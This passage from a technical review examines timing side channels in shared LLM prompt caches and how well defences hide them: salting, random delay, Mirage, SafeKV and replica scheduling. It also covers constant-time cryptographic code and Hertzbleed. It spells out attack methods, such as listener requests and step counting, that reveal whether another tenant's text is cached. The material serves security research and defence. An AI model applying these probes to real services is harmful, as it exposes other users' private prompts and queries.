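The engines they study are work-conserving, which means they never sit idle while a request is waiting. If a guess hits the cache, it needs less computation, and every request queued behind it starts earlier by the full time saved.

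Sun and Xiao sent a guess with a 1,024-token prefix to an idle vLLM engine running an 8-billion-parameter model on an L40S GPU, followed by 16 requests with unrelated text, which they call listeners. Prefill for 1,024 tokens takes about 68 milliseconds on this GPU. When the prefix was in the cache, all 16 listeners finished 68 to 69 milliseconds earlier. The attacker could therefore measure a single saving 16 times, and the waits became shorter by about 1.1 seconds in total. A service that disguised only the timing of the guess would not change the timing of the listeners.

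The same idea can reveal a match of just one block. On this GPU, each vLLM step processes up to 2,048 tokens. The attacker first sends a long request to keep the engine busy, so that the guess and a listener wait in the queue together. They choose the lengths so that the two exactly fill one step if the guess hits. For example, suppose the guess has 16 tokens to test plus 1,000 fresh ones, and the listener has 1,048:

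| | Tested block is in the cache | It is not |
|---|---|---|
| Work for the guess | 1,000 tokens | 1,016 tokens |
| Work for the listener | 1,048 tokens | 1,048 tokens |
| Total | 2,048, which fits in one step | 2,064, which is 16 too many |
| Delay before the listener's reply | About 153 ms | 304 to 309 ms |

The listener's last 16 tokens spill over into the next step, and a final request of 2,048 tokens fills that step. This turns a difference of about a millisecond in computation into one of about 150 milliseconds. With these four requests, the attacker's advantage was at least 0.985. In a similar experiment with a 16-token match, timing the guess itself gave an advantage of only 0.07.

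On a busy engine, other customers' requests change how long the attacker waits, so the attacker counts the engine's steps instead of milliseconds. Requests that complete prefill in the same step get their first token together. If the attacker sends probe requests limited to one output token each, the replies arrive in clusters, one per step.

To test whether a 1,024-token text was cached, Sun and Xiao sent 52 requests in a short burst, with 176-token listeners before and after the guess. A full step holds 11 or 12 listeners. The clusters before the guess show where the next step should end if the guess hits the cache. If it misses, its 1,024 tokens take up half the step, which then ends about six listeners earlier.

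Sun and Xiao tested the method on one vLLM instance while replaying real traffic from Microsoft's Azure service. With load at up to half the engine's capacity, a single test had an advantage of at least 0.98 for texts of 256, 1,024 or 4,096 tokens. For 1,024-token texts under load, the guess's own time to first token (TTFT) gave an advantage of at most 0.19. An earlier version of the test had scored as low as 0.50 on 256-token texts, so they corrected its design. They then repeated the corrected experiment with every setting frozen and got the same result.

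A positive result is less reliable when few of the candidate texts are in the cache. Only one of 782 tests wrongly reported that a text was cached, but if one candidate in 1,000 is actually cached, these tests show only that a positive result is right at least 14% of the time.

### Several servers, and a document search

Large services run many copies of a model, and the attack gets weaker when the attacker's guess may go to a different copy from the one that handled the other user's text. In the table, each pair of numbers gives the attacker's advantage at a quarter and at half of capacity.

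| Set-up | 1,024-token text | 4,096-token text |
|---|---|---|
| Two instances, router sends requests to the best cached match | 0.88, 0.87 | 0.98, 0.94 |
| Four instances, same routing | 0.71, 0.60 | 0.90, 0.98 |
| Two instances in rotation, one guess | 0.45, 0.45 | |
| Four instances in rotation, one guess | 0.02, 0.11 | |
| Four instances in rotation, one guess for each | 0.41, 0.34 | 0.62, 0.74 |

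Sending requests to each instance in turn makes the attack much harder, but it also makes honest customers' requests miss the cached copy as often as the attacker's do.

Sun and Xiao also tested a case closer to what agents do. A victim asked private questions of a system that searches 48 Wikipedia articles, split into 429 passages, and gives the most relevant passages to the model. The attacker had to pick which of four passages the system had retrieved first, and was right 97% of the time on an idle engine, 95% at a quarter of capacity and 85% at half, compared with 25% by chance. The passages are public, but the choice among them depends on the private question, so the attacker learns what the victim asked about. The attacker had the advantage of knowing when the victim asked.

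The attack has important limits:

- It shows only whether somebody recently used a text the attacker already has. It does not identify the user, and under load it has not recovered unknown text.
- The victim's entry must still be in the cache. At three quarters of capacity, the advantage fell to between 0.66 and 0.98, and when the cache was nearly full, the engine had already evicted the entry in 26% to 32% of the relevant trials.
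- Engines that process more tokens per step hide short texts better. On GPUs with a default budget of 8,192 tokens, the advantage for a 1,024-token text was at most 0.45.
- The reading is guaranteed to be correct only if no other request arrives during the burst.

To estimate how often the last condition holds, suppose other requests arrive at random at an average rate of $\lambda$ per second. The chance that none arrives in a window of $w$ seconds is then $e^{-\lambda w}$. At half of capacity, $\lambda$ was about 2.27, so an 80% chance of a quiet window requires $w$ to be about 98 milliseconds. Of these, 22 are unavoidable, leaving 76 to send 51 requests. If a provider enforces its limits second by second, the attacker needs an allowance of about 3,000 requests per minute, or several accounts. If other customers send more than ten requests per second, even an instantaneous burst has less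 than an 80% chance of avoiding interruption. This estimate is cautious, because many interruptions are harmless to the attack. In one analysis, 24 of 44 interruptions misled the attacker when the interrupting request's length was within a critical range, but only 3 of 180 did when it was outside that range.

Sun and Xiao did not test any commercial service. If a service keeps each account's cache separate, an attacker cannot use the cache to learn about text from other accounts.

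### Cache salting and where it stops

The usual way to separate caches is cache salting, which adds a secret or tenant-specific value $\sigma$ to the first key:

$$h_0 = H(\sigma,\ \text{tokens}_{0..15}).$$

Every later key depends on the first, so salting the first key makes all of a tenant's keys different from other tenants' keys. An attacker who sends exactly the victim's text then gets a cache miss. vLLM accepts a salt with each request. Salting doesn't protect semantic caches, which match by meaning instead of by key, and it doesn't hide total memory use from someone who measures inter-token latency (ITL).

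Salting stops tenants from reusing one another's cached computation. Gu and colleagues expected this to matter little because different users seldom send prompts with long identical openings, but everyone who uses the same coding agent sends the same thousands of tokens of instructions. On the Llama-2-70B layout, a 2,000-token opening takes up 0.66 gigabytes. If 100 tenants use it at once with salting, the server must store 100 copies, or 66 gigabytes, and compute each one separately.

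A compromise is to add the salt after the public opening of the prompt, so that tenants share only the standard instructions. vLLM's salt doesn't allow this, because it applies from the start of the prompt. Addagada estimates that the compromise would keep 93% of the saving in TTFT for a prompt with 2,000 public tokens and 119 private ones. In a replay of 5,713 requests, Sun and colleagues found that such a split raised modelled costs by 1.7% to 2.5%. An attacker could still learn that someone is using a particular set of instructions, which is harmless for a popular coding agent but perhaps not for a company's confidential template.

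A salt separates only the parties that the service can tell apart. A provider sees accounts, so it can't distinguish the users of Song and colleagues' document summariser, or customers whom a gateway has put under one account. Opening more accounts is not always possible. According to Sun and colleagues, Anthropic separates caches by workspace and allows 100 workspaces per organisation, so a gateway with more than 100 customers has to put some of them in the same workspace.

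The software that knows who the end users are therefore has to pass this information to the engine, which has to use it. Sun and Xiao recommend an interface that accepts a separate isolation key for each group of users who trust one another. Fahey points out that OpenAI's existing "prompt_cache_key" setting isn't enough, because it only influences which server handles a request, and two users can still end up on the same one. Every layer between that software and the engine also has to preserve the information. When Sun and colleagues chained two gateways, the inner one could overwrite the customer's identity and restore the sharing that the outer one had prevented.

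Suppose an insurer runs one agent for all its policyholders under a single account. A cache salt for that account prevents other companies from probing its cache, but one policyholder could still upload a document to test whether another had submitted the same one. A separate salt for each policyholder would prevent this. The agent could no longer reuse cached computation across policyholders, but it would still avoid recomputing its growing context at every step of a task.

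## Whether a shared cache can hide its hits

Giving every policyholder a separate salt slows responses because requests can no longer reuse text cached for other policyholders. In *Selective KV-Cache Sharing to Mitigate Timing Side-Channels in LLM Inference*, Chu, Lin and colleagues (2025) found that requests in three collections of prompts could reuse 9%, 25% and 63% of their text from other users' requests. Giving each user a separate cache raised time to first token (TTFT) by 2% to 9% on a 13-billion-parameter model and by 8% to 39% on a 70-billion-parameter model. Several designs therefore keep one cache for everybody and try to make a hit look like a miss.

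Sun and Xiao define success at this as a form of noninterference. They compare a world in which the victim has sent a certain text with one in which the victim sent an equally long text that nobody else uses. The cache hides its hits if everything other tenants observe from then on is equally likely in both worlds. $\text{Obs}$ here includes the arrival time of every token of every later request, along with bills, usage counts and refusals. A hit can change these observations in at least four ways:

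| What the hit affects | What changes |
|---|---|
| The request that hits | It starts sooner, and may cost less |
| Requests queued behind it | They start and finish earlier |
| Shared state | Other entries stay in the cache longer, and a defence's own records change |
| The hardware | The GPU idles for a moment, and later steps run faster |

Most published designs address only the first row.

### Adding random delay

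The simplest idea is to add timing noise so that hits and misses are harder to tell apart. Addagada tried this as one component of a defence called KVGov, in a simulation where a hit took 5 milliseconds and a miss took 50. Gaussian noise with a standard deviation of 20 milliseconds cut the success rate of PromptPeek from 100% to 0.3% (0.5% in the paper's text). InputSnatch still succeeded every time, but it was counted as a success whenever the text was in the cache, so noise could not have affected the result. KVGov's main protection is a salt for each tenant, which stopped both attacks on its own.

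The result for PromptPeek depends heavily on the test that the simulated attacker used, which required a correlation of at least 0.85 between two sets of timings. A plain threshold would have worked much better. If the attacker calls anything under 27.5 milliseconds a hit, the noise has to exceed 22.5 milliseconds, or 1.125 standard deviations, to cause an error. Let $\Phi(x)$ be the probability that a standard Gaussian variable is below $x$. With no other source of variation, the advantage from one measurement is

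$$2\Phi(1.125) - 1 \approx 0.74 .$$

On a real A100, Addagada measured a gap of 117 milliseconds for a long prefix, and the same calculation gives an advantage above 0.99.

Noise is even less effective against an attacker who times the requests queued behind the guess. Call the amount by which a hit brings those requests forward the shift, $s$. Sun and Xiao consider an attacker who places $k$ listeners in the engine step before the guess and $k$ in the step after it, then compares the average reply times of the two groups. If the service adds independent Gaussian noise with standard deviation $\sigma$ to each reply, and the engine's own timing varies with standard deviation $\sigma_e$, the advantage is at least

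$$2\Phi\left(\frac{s}{2\sqrt{\sigma_e^2 + 2\sigma^2/k}}\right) - 1 .$$

The attacker can arrange the requests so that even a 16-token hit shifts a listener by a full step, about 156 milliseconds. With $\sigma = 20$ milliseconds, negligible engine noise and one listener on each side, the formula gives 0.994.

In tests on an idle engine, KVGov's noise left the listeners an advantage of about 0.99 for hits of 1,024 tokens or more. It reduced the advantage to 0.67 for a 256-token hit whose shift was only 10 milliseconds. Under load, the noise at first reduced the attack's advantage to between 0.41 and 0.95 by disrupting how the attacker sorted replies into steps. When the attacker sorted them by the engine's regular rhythm instead, the advantage returned to at least 0.987 at loads up to half of capacity.

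Sun and Xiao also measured how much delay would be enough. They added independent random delays from an exponential distribution, which are mostly short but occasionally long. The mean delay had to be 9 to 16 times the shift to cut the advantage to 0.1. For a 1,024-token hit, the shift is 69 milliseconds, so the service would have to delay every reply by roughly 0.6 to 1.1 seconds on average to hide it.

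A cleverer attacker would force the delays higher still. Some of the exponential delays are very short, so the attacker can compare the earliest reply in each group instead of the average. The advantage is then at least

$$1 - e^{-ks/(2\mu)},$$

where $\mu$ is the mean delay. With eight listeners on each side, keeping this below 0.1 requires $\mu$ to be about 38 times the shift, or 2.6 seconds for the 1,024-token hit.

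These results assume that the service draws each delay independently. Sun and Xiao extend the Gaussian result to one kind of correlated delay, but leave open what happens if, for example, the service delays all replies after a certain moment by the same random amount.

### Delaying the whole reply after suspicious probing

Yan and Zhang's Mirage avoids delaying everyone by watching for the pattern that guessing produces. An attacker who wants to recover unknown text has to try many different continuations of the same opening. Mirage keeps a score for each sensitive opening, or prefix, and each user. With the default settings, a request that arrives $\Delta t$ seconds after the previous one updates the score as follows:

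$$S \leftarrow 0.995^{\Delta t} S + \phi ,$$

where $\phi$ is 1 for a continuation that Mirage has not seen before and 0 for a repeat. The score also has an upper limit, so that an attacker can't lock a prefix indefinitely with one flood of requests.

Suppose an attacker knows that a prompt begins "The patient suffers from" and tries "asthma". The score becomes 1, which does not exceed the threshold of 1, so the reply goes out at its natural speed. One second later the attacker tries "diabetes". The score rises to 1.995 and Mirage puts the prefix in lockdown. If the attacker makes no further guesses, the score takes about 138 seconds to fall back to the threshold.

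In lockdown, the engine still uses the shared cache, but the gateway in front of it holds the reply. The gateway estimates how long a genuine miss of that length takes under the current load, and sets a target slower than about 97% of misses, with a further 20% margin. If the first token is ready before the target, the gateway holds it until then and delays every later token by the same amount. For example, if tokens are ready at 150, 166 and 182 milliseconds and the target is 418, they go out at 418, 434 and 450. If the gateway held only the first token, the others would come out in a burst right after it, which would reveal the hit.

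Yan and Zhang tested Mirage against three attacks. One of them, OptiLeak, reads the order in which replies return, as PromptPeek does. The success rates for a 14-billion-parameter model were:

| Attack | No defence | Mirage | Separate cache per tenant |
|---|---|---|---|
| Early Bird | 92.4% | 0.2% | 0.5% |
| InputSnatch | 59.4% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| OptiLeak | 68.8% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Mirage was also much faster than separate caches when the engine was busy. With 64 tenants sharing one sensitive prefix near the engine's capacity, the time to first token was 542 milliseconds with no defence, 611 with Mirage and 1,858 with separate caches. In another test, an ordinary user's first request took 150 milliseconds with Mirage, almost the same as with no defence.

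A small timing difference remained in lockdown. A classifier trained on 20 repeated TTFT measurements scored an AUC of 0.53, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. Yan and Zhang convert this to a leak of at most $2 \times 0.53 - 1 = 0.06$ bits per probe, or at least 17 probes per bit. But another of their classifiers, using only the gaps between tokens, scored 0.63 on the 14-billion-parameter model. The same conversion gives 0.26 bits per probe, or about four probes per bit. Some of that may be sampling noise, since their reported scores cannot fall below 0.5, but 0.06 bits per probe is still not a safe upper limit on the leak.

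Mirage is better suited to stopping reconstruction than membership tests. By default, it does not delay the first new continuation. Yan and Zhang reason that one guess reveals very little about a long secret, which is true if the attacker has to reconstruct it. But someone who already has a merger document needs only one guess to learn whether a law firm has uploaded it. Mirage can delay the first guess too, but then an ordinary user's first request takes 417 milliseconds instead of 150.

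Another likely weakness is that Mirage pools anonymous users under one score but gives each authenticated user their own. An attacker with twenty verified accounts would seem to get twenty undelayed guesses. Using one score for everyone would prevent this, but in a test of that setting, Mirage delayed 93% of legitimate requests that continued a shared prefix in different ways. Those requests took 87 milliseconds instead of 25.

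Yan and Zhang also considered an attacker who waits between guesses. In an idealised test where the score reset to zero each time and the victim's text stayed in the cache, the attack succeeded 76.5% of the time. They dismiss this as unrealistic because a busy engine would evict the text during the long waits. Whether the text would be evicted depends on the provider. According to Sun and Xiao, providers describe keeping entries for between about five minutes and 24 hours.

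### Whether Mirage answers the listeners

Sun and Xiao published their objection to this kind of defence in November 2026, the same month as Mirage. They imagined a perfect version, in which everything about the guess looks like a miss but the engine's scheduling stays the same. Their attack never uses the reply to the guess, so it worked as well as before. A single guess gave an advantage of 0.96 to 0.99 on idle vLLM and SGLang engines. Users whose replies were already streaming could also detect the hit, because their next six tokens arrived 8 to 279 milliseconds sooner.

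Mirage deliberately leaves the scheduler unchanged. It is efficient because the GPU can process other requests while the gateway holds the disguised reply, which in one test gave about 1.6 times the throughput of separate caches. As a result, those other requests finish earlier, and the listeners measure when they finish.

Yan and Zhang designed a mechanism in Mirage that acts across requests to stop attacks that read the order of replies. The gateway groups simultaneous replies under the same locked prefix, even if they belong to different accounts. It holds them until the group has been quiet for a short interval, then releases each after its own random delay. The reply to a correct guess therefore no longer stands out by arriving first.

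This probably doesn't stop the listeners. Sun and Xiao fill their listeners with fresh random tokens, so a listener doesn't begin with the locked prefix or join the group. Mirage would treat it as public traffic or as the first continuation of some other prefix. Either way, the reply would go out as soon as it was ready, and its timing would still show the hit.

The answer is less clear if the provider treats a whole service as sensitive, which Yan and Zhang recommend as the safe setting. If every request to the service began with the same monitored text, the listeners would count as new continuations of it. They would soon trigger the lockdown, and Mirage would delay and shuffle them too. But the target time is only a minimum, so an attacker could queue enough work ahead of the listeners to push them past it. Sun and Xiao prove that a simpler minimum of this kind leaves listeners some advantage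 whenever a listener that misses the cache can take longer than the minimum to be ready. Mirage's grouping and random delays would make the signal harder to read, perhaps much harder.

Both conclusions are inferences from the two designs. Yan and Zhang did not test Mirage against listeners, and Sun and Xiao did not examine it.

### Sharing only some of the cache

Other designs restrict what tenants share instead of changing the timing. Chu and colleagues' SafeKV makes every new block private to its creator, then checks in the background whether the block is safe to share. Simple rules detect patterns such as email addresses and card numbers. A small language model examines what the rules don't flag, and if its result is uncertain, the main model decides using the recent conversation. Fewer than 8% of requests needed this last check.

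SafeKV recovered much of the speed lost by separating caches. In conversations with one large model, separate caches raised time to first token by 50% over full sharing, while SafeKV raised it by 12%. Its throughput was 1.36 to 2.66 times that of separate caches. In over 94% of time windows on average, the attacker could not reliably tell hits from misses on sensitive text.

The classifier is the weak point. The small model was about 97% accurate on ordinary examples but only about 50% accurate on longer prompts where privacy depended on context. The strongest main model raised this to over 90%. Chu and colleagues estimate the chance that a sensitive block becomes shareable by multiplying the three stages' miss rates:

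$$P_{\text{leak}} = \alpha_1 \cdot \alpha_{2|1} \cdot \alpha_{3|12} .$$

This holds only if each stage checks everything the earlier stages missed. When the small model is confidently wrong, the block never reaches the main model, so the last factor is effectively 1.

SafeKV also monitors how blocks are reused and can make a shared block private again. It divides the number of distinct users by the number of hits, so 20 hits from two users give 0.1 and 20 hits from 20 users give 1. The paper's design treats an unusually high ratio as suspicious for a block that previously had one user, but its security analysis treats a persistently low ratio as suspicious. The first rule might catch an attacker who uses many accounts, and the second might catch one who repeats a guess from a single account, but neither can be triggered before the first successful guess.

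*CacheSolidarity* (Pennas, Papaioannou and colleagues, 2026) records which user created each block instead of classifying text. When another user's request first hits a block, the system serves it normally and flags the block, then refuses later hits across users. A component called the Activator turns this protection on only when the latencies of hits and misses differ enough to distinguish them. Compared with separate caches, the system allowed up to 70% more reuse and reduced latency by up to 30%.

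Sun and Xiao tested the public code with the protection always on. They first fixed a bug that left old flags on reused blocks and made the system refuse unrelated hits at random. Since the system allows the first hit, an attacker could detect it with an advantage of about 0.98. The flags also created a new leak. When the victim's request reuses a block, it leaves a flag, which changes how much of a later guess can hit. The attacker could detect this change with an advantage of 0.97 to 0.98.

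Nobody has tested the Activator against listeners, because the public code didn't include it. Pennas and colleagues found that heavy load makes the TTFTs of hits and misses nearly indistinguishable, but their premise for the Activator, that the leak is then gone, looks doubtful. Sun and Xiao's listeners could detect hits at loads where the guess's own TTFT revealed little about 1,024-token texts. An Activator that relied only on TTFT might therefore turn the protection off while the attack still worked.

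Even a perfect classifier would leave some private information exposed, because a private question can determine which public text the model reads, as in the search of Wikipedia articles. If the insurance agent retrieves a public guide about making claims after a drink-driving conviction, SafeKV could reasonably share it, but an attacker who finds it in the cache learns that some customer's question led the agent to retrieve it.

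### A visible benefit is also a signal

These designs fail for the same reason. A tenant benefits from sharing only if something the tenant can observe improves, such as the speed of a reply, and an attacker can observe the same improvement. Sun and Xiao use this to derive a limit on any possible design.

Let $\varepsilon$ be the largest advantage that the provider permits an attacker to have when testing for one text. Suppose $k$ other accounts use a text that could benefit tenant $b$. Now replace the text in the first account's requests with random tokens. Tenant $b$ could be an attacker, so the replacement can change the probabilities of what $b$ observes by at most $\varepsilon$. Do the same for the second account, and so on. After $k$ replacements nobody else uses the text, and $b$ gets no benefit from sharing it. The total change is at most $k\varepsilon$. If the benefit is a quantity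 that varies over a range of size $R$, such as a latency between zero and a timeout, then

$$\text{average gain} \le R\,k\,\varepsilon .$$

Suppose latency can range from 0 to 2 seconds and the provider permits an advantage of $\varepsilon = 0.01$. If one other account uses the text, sharing can save $b$ at most 20 milliseconds on average, less than a third of the 68 milliseconds that a 1,024-token hit saves on the L40S GPU. If ten other accounts use it, the limit rises to 200 milliseconds, which is more than such a hit saves and so doesn't restrict it. The theorem therefore doesn't rule out sharing very popular text at a small risk to each user, although it doesn't show that any design achieves this. If $\varepsilon$ is exactly zero, sharing saves $b$ no time, however popular the text is.

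One defence based on popularity comes from file storage, where a service can wait until a secret random number of accounts have uploaded a file before it shares one copy. In a text cache, this would limit the advantage an attacker gains from their own guess to about one divided by the number of possible thresholds. But an attacker with enough accounts can send the text from all of them until the cache starts sharing it. If the attacker also knows when the victim is active, the listeners can then detect the victim's own hit.

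### Running in step with a replica

Zero leakage is possible in principle. Sun and Xiao describe a design in which the provider runs a replica of the engine's scheduler. The replica receives the same requests but treats every hit on another tenant's text as a miss. It works out when each step would start and end, without doing the step's computation. The real engine uses the cached text, finishes early, waits for the replica's step to end and releases everything at the replica's times.

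For example, a full step of 2,048 tokens takes about 153 milliseconds on an L40S. If 1,024 of the tokens are in the cache, the engine needs only about 85 milliseconds. It then idles for the other 68, so every tenant sees the same timing as for a miss. No tenant benefits from the saved time, as the theorem requires, but the provider can use it to save energy or to run its own work, as long as that work never delays a customer.

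The waiting also costs something, because the provider cannot know exactly how long the skipped work would have taken. The replica's steps have to last long enough to cover this uncertainty. The provider also has to pad every step that might contain a hit, whether or not it does, since selective padding would reveal the hits. Let $w$ be the uncertainty as a share of a full step's duration $d$. Each such step then adds a pause of $wd$. If every step might contain a hit, the pauses add up to the 68 milliseconds saved by one 1,024-token hit after $n$ steps, where $nwd = 68$ milliseconds. The time this takes is

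$$nd = \frac{68\ \text{ms}}{w} .$$

| Uncertainty $w$ | Time until pauses cancel one 1,024-token hit | One 4,096-token hit |
|---|---|---|
| 0.13% (measured step times, best case) | 52 s | 231 s |
| 0.77% (measured step times, worst case) | 8.8 s | 39 s |
| 8% (fitted formula, best case) | 0.85 s | 3.8 s |
| 16% (fitted formula, worst case) | 0.43 s | 1.9 s |

Sun and Xiao round the range for the 1,024-token hit to between 0.4 and 50 seconds. Total pause time keeps growing, but more hits reduce the pause time per hit. With one such hit per second, the provider would save 68 milliseconds of GPU time each second and lose 1.3 milliseconds to pauses in the best case, or 160 in the worst. The savings and losses aren't fully comparable, because the pauses reduce how many customers the engine can serve, while the saved time can't be used to serve customers.

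Fixed deadlines may hide hits less well than the best case suggests. Sun and Xiao released simulated steps at fixed deadlines and found that the GPU ran faster after the idle time left by a hit, so steps missed their deadlines less often after hits. This gave an attacker an advantage of 0.98 with no safety margin and 0.55 with a 2% margin. A 5% margin appeared to work in the first run, but in a repetition, margins of 3%, 5% and 7% left advantages between 0.19 and 0.57, though a 4% margin left no detectable advantage. They traced the leak in the repetition to the release timers, whose overshoot varied with the idle time by about 10 microseconds on average.

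The guarantee of zero leakage therefore depends on demanding conditions:

- **Step times don't depend on content.** The theorems assume dense models, which use all their parameters for every token. Mixture-of-experts models choose different parameters for different tokens, so a step's duration can depend on the text. The listener attack still worked on one such model.
- **There is only one engine instance.** Sun and Xiao have not proved the result for several instances, or measured the attack on instances that share one cache.
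- **Release times are exact.** Every real step must also finish within the time set for the replica's step.
- **A request's output doesn't depend on the other requests in the batch.** This requires special numerical routines, called batch-invariant kernels.
- **The victim's behaviour doesn't reveal the text.** The length of the victim's replies must be fixed, and the timing, length and settings of later requests must not depend on what the replies say.

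The limit on a tenant's gain applies only to tenants within the provider's ordinary rate limits. A provider may be able to pass savings on to larger customers while hiding them from everyone else. The padding estimate also leaves out schedulers that reorder requests. A provider that learns the exact duration of frequently repeated steps would need less padding.

The condition on the victim's behaviour excludes most agents, because an agent chooses its next call based on the last reply. Sun and Xiao point out that this dependence can reveal a secret even when every account has its own salt.

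## Constant-time code and the parts of inference it can protect

A defence such as Mirage lets secret text change how much work the engine does, and is designed to hide the difference. Cryptographers usually write programs that do the same work whatever the secret is instead.

Constant-time coding began as a response to the attack on RSA and similar systems described in Kocher's 1996 paper *Timing Attacks on Implementations of Diffie-Hellman, RSA, DSS, and Other Systems*. The attack needs little computing power and often requires only known encrypted messages.

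RSA and Diffie-Hellman both compute $a^b \bmod n$, where the exponent $b$ is secret. The simplest method goes through the binary digits of $b$ from left to right. It squares a running result at every digit and also multiplies it by $a$ if the digit is 1:

| Secret exponent | Work for each digit | Operations |
|---|---|---|
| 13 (binary 1101) | Square and multiply; square and multiply; square; square and multiply | 7 |
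| 8 (binary 1000) | Square and multiply; square; square; square | 5 |

The total time reveals how many digits are 1, and an attacker who can time each step can recover the key. Intel's *Guidelines for Mitigating Timing Side Channels Against Cryptographic Implementations* (2022) give a simple fix that multiplies at every digit, by $a$ if the digit is 1 and by 1 if it is 0. This takes three multiplications per digit instead of an average of 1.5.

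### Three rules

Arranz-Olmos, Barthe and colleagues, in *Let's DOIT*, summarise constant-time programming in three rules:

1. Never branch on a condition that depends on a secret.
2. Never access memory at an address that depends on a secret.
3. Never use arithmetic whose running time varies with its inputs on secret data.

The standard example for the first rule, which Schneider, Lain and colleagues (2024), in *Breaking Bad*, also use, is a choice between two values. The obvious version branches on the secret bit:

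```
if bit == 1: result = x
else:        result = y
```

The constant-time version calculates the answer with the same instructions either way:

```
mask   = -bit
result = (x AND mask) OR (y AND NOT mask)
```

Computers normally represent −1 as a row of ones, so the mask is all ones when the bit is 1 and all zeros when it is 0. With the four-digit values $x = 1010$ and $y = 0110$, this gives:

| | Bit is 1 | Bit is 0 |
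|---|---|---|
| `mask` | 1111 | 0000 |
| `x AND mask` | 1010 | 0000 |
| `y AND NOT mask` | 0000 | 0110 |
| `result` | 1010, which is `x` | 0110, which is `y` |

A loop that repeats a secret number of times must be handled the same way. The 2022 programming guide *I'm writing software. What can I do to protect against timing attacks?* recommends running the loop the maximum possible number of times and then selecting the correct result.

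The second rule matters because recently used memory is faster to read. Processors cache memory in blocks called cache lines. The encryption standard AES uses a public table of 256 bytes, which spans four cache lines on most processors. According to Intel, detecting which line a lookup touched gives a spy program two bits of information about a secret key. A program can prevent this leak by reading the whole table every time and keeping only the entry it needs.

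The third rule applies to division, which takes a variable time on many processors, and to multiplication on some older Arm chips. In the KyberSlash attack, researchers recovered private keys from implementations of Kyber, an encryption scheme meant to resist quantum computers, because the code divided a number that depended on the secret.

These rules do not make the running time constant. Encrypting a long message still takes longer than encrypting a short one, which the rules allow because they treat the length as public. In Intel's example, a naive password check stops at the first wrong letter, so an attacker who can time it can find a four-letter lowercase password one letter at a time, in at most 104 guesses instead of up to 456,976. The corrected check compares every letter, which removes this leak, but it still takes longer for longer inputs. If the length is also secret, the program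 has to pad the input. *Constant-Time Code* (Pornin, 2025) accepts the traditional name but offers "achronognostic", meaning that there is no knowledge in time, as a more exact one.

The rules amount to noninterference with $\text{Obs}$ defined as the instructions a program executes, the memory addresses it accesses and the inputs to any variable-time instructions. If two secrets produce the same $\text{Obs}$, the running time should also be the same. This holds only if the compiler preserves the programmer's instructions and nothing else about the secret affects the processor's speed, and both assumptions have failed in practice.

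### Failures in compilers and processors

A compiler turns source code into processor instructions, and it may replace any calculation with a faster one that gives the same result. Pornin demonstrates this with a function from the encryption library BearSSL that uses masks to copy one array over another only if a secret value is non-zero. The technique worked in around 2015, but version 18 of the Clang compiler detects the test and inserts a branch that skips the copying when the value is zero. Pornin doesn't consider this a defect, because compilers are meant to find such shortcuts.

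Schneider and colleagues measured how common the problem is. They compiled eight cryptographic libraries for six types of processor, using many versions of two popular compilers, and compared each program's behaviour with different keys. After filtering out known faults in the source code, they found at least one secret-dependent branch in 7.5% of the 5,716 compiled programs and at least one secret-dependent memory access in 6.4%. The affected libraries included HACL\*, whose source code had been formally verified against such leaks. They didn't test whether an attacker could exploit each leak, and they may have missed some leaks because they ran each program only a few times.

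Checking the source code can't reveal these faults, so developers have to check the compiled program. One method is to mark the secrets as uninitialised memory and run the program under Valgrind, a debugging tool that reports any branch or address that depends on that memory. This method finds faults only on the paths that the program takes during the test.

Processors can introduce timing leaks even when the compiler does not. For decades, programmers had no guarantee that an instruction with a fixed running time on current chips would also have one on future chips. Arm (in 2020) and Intel (in 2022) introduced modes that guarantee that the running time of a listed set of instructions does not depend on the data. RISC-V processors have a comparable guarantee that does not require enabling a mode.

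Arranz-Olmos and colleagues found hardly any software that used the Arm or Intel modes. They also found that Arm had repeatedly removed instructions from its list of constant-time instructions, which makes the guarantee less useful for future chips. On Intel processors, only the operating system kernel can turn the mode on. According to Pornin, the listed Intel instructions still ran in constant time without the mode as of early 2025, but the mode also disables a feature that fetches memory in advance based on data values. Researchers have exploited a similar feature on Apple chips.

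Hertzbleed is a more fundamental problem, because it affects programs whose instructions all behave as promised. A program that needs $n$ clock cycles at frequency $f$ takes

$$t = \frac{n}{f}$$

seconds. The three rules keep $n$ independent of the secret. Modern processors, however, adjust $f$ to stay within limits on power and heat, and power consumption depends on the data. Three billion cycles take 1 second at 3 gigahertz and about 1.03 seconds at 2.9.

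Wang, Paccagnella and colleagues (2022), in *Hertzbleed*, used this effect to extract complete keys remotely from constant-time implementations of SIKE, another scheme meant to resist quantum computers. They chose messages that made thousands of operations use more or less power depending on whether a guess about a single key bit was right. Other researchers have since broken SIKE by unrelated means, but follow-up work described on the attack's website, *Hertzbleed Attack*, extended the attack to other cryptosystems and to programs outside cryptography. Turning off the processor's frequency boost usually stops the leak but slows the processor significantly.

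The researchers concluded that current guidelines for constant-time code are insufficient. The programming guide rejects the stronger claim that Hertzbleed undermines constant-time programming. It argues that a fixed clock frequency was always part of preventing secrets from affecting timing. The two sides mostly disagree about what constant-time programming includes. Either way, code that follows the three rules but runs at a variable clock frequency is not safe from Hertzbleed.

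### Whether the rules are still worth following

Pornin expects the problem to get worse because compilers keep improving, and just-in-time compilers, which translate a program while it runs, also have access to its data. If a program encrypts many messages with one key, such a compiler might treat the key as a constant and optimise the code for it. Some processors have translated code this way internally, where outside developers cannot inspect the result. Pornin therefore considers it infeasible to write source code that runs in constant time on most machines, though it remains possible for a simple chip or one with explicit timing guarantees.

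An obvious response would be to settle for weaker rules. Brumley (2026), in *SoK*, compares five versions of the constant-time model, most of which allow some exceptions:

| Model | What it permits | What went wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Program counter, 2004–2005 | Secret-dependent memory addresses | Attackers recovered keys through the data cache |
| Traditional, 2004–2006 | No secret-dependent branches or addresses | Compilers added branches, and some instructions varied in time |
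| Intel scatter-gather, 2005 | Secret-dependent addresses within one cache line | The CacheBleed attack detected differences inside a line |
| OpenSSL, 2019 | Leaks that only someone on the same machine can measure | Most cache attacks fall outside the policy |
| BoringSSL, 2025 | Leaks from inputs of variable length | Loading time revealed the length of a stored private key |

Brumley concludes that every relaxation of the traditional model has eventually been exploited. The BoringSSL case is weak support for this, since it affects only private keys stored in a non-standard shortened form, and Brumley knows of no attack that could use the leak. But it does show that a stricter policy does not guarantee a smaller leak. BoringSSL's policy is stricter than OpenSSL's, yet one timing measurement revealed about 0.61 bits of information about a key's length in BoringSSL and 0.003 in OpenSSL.

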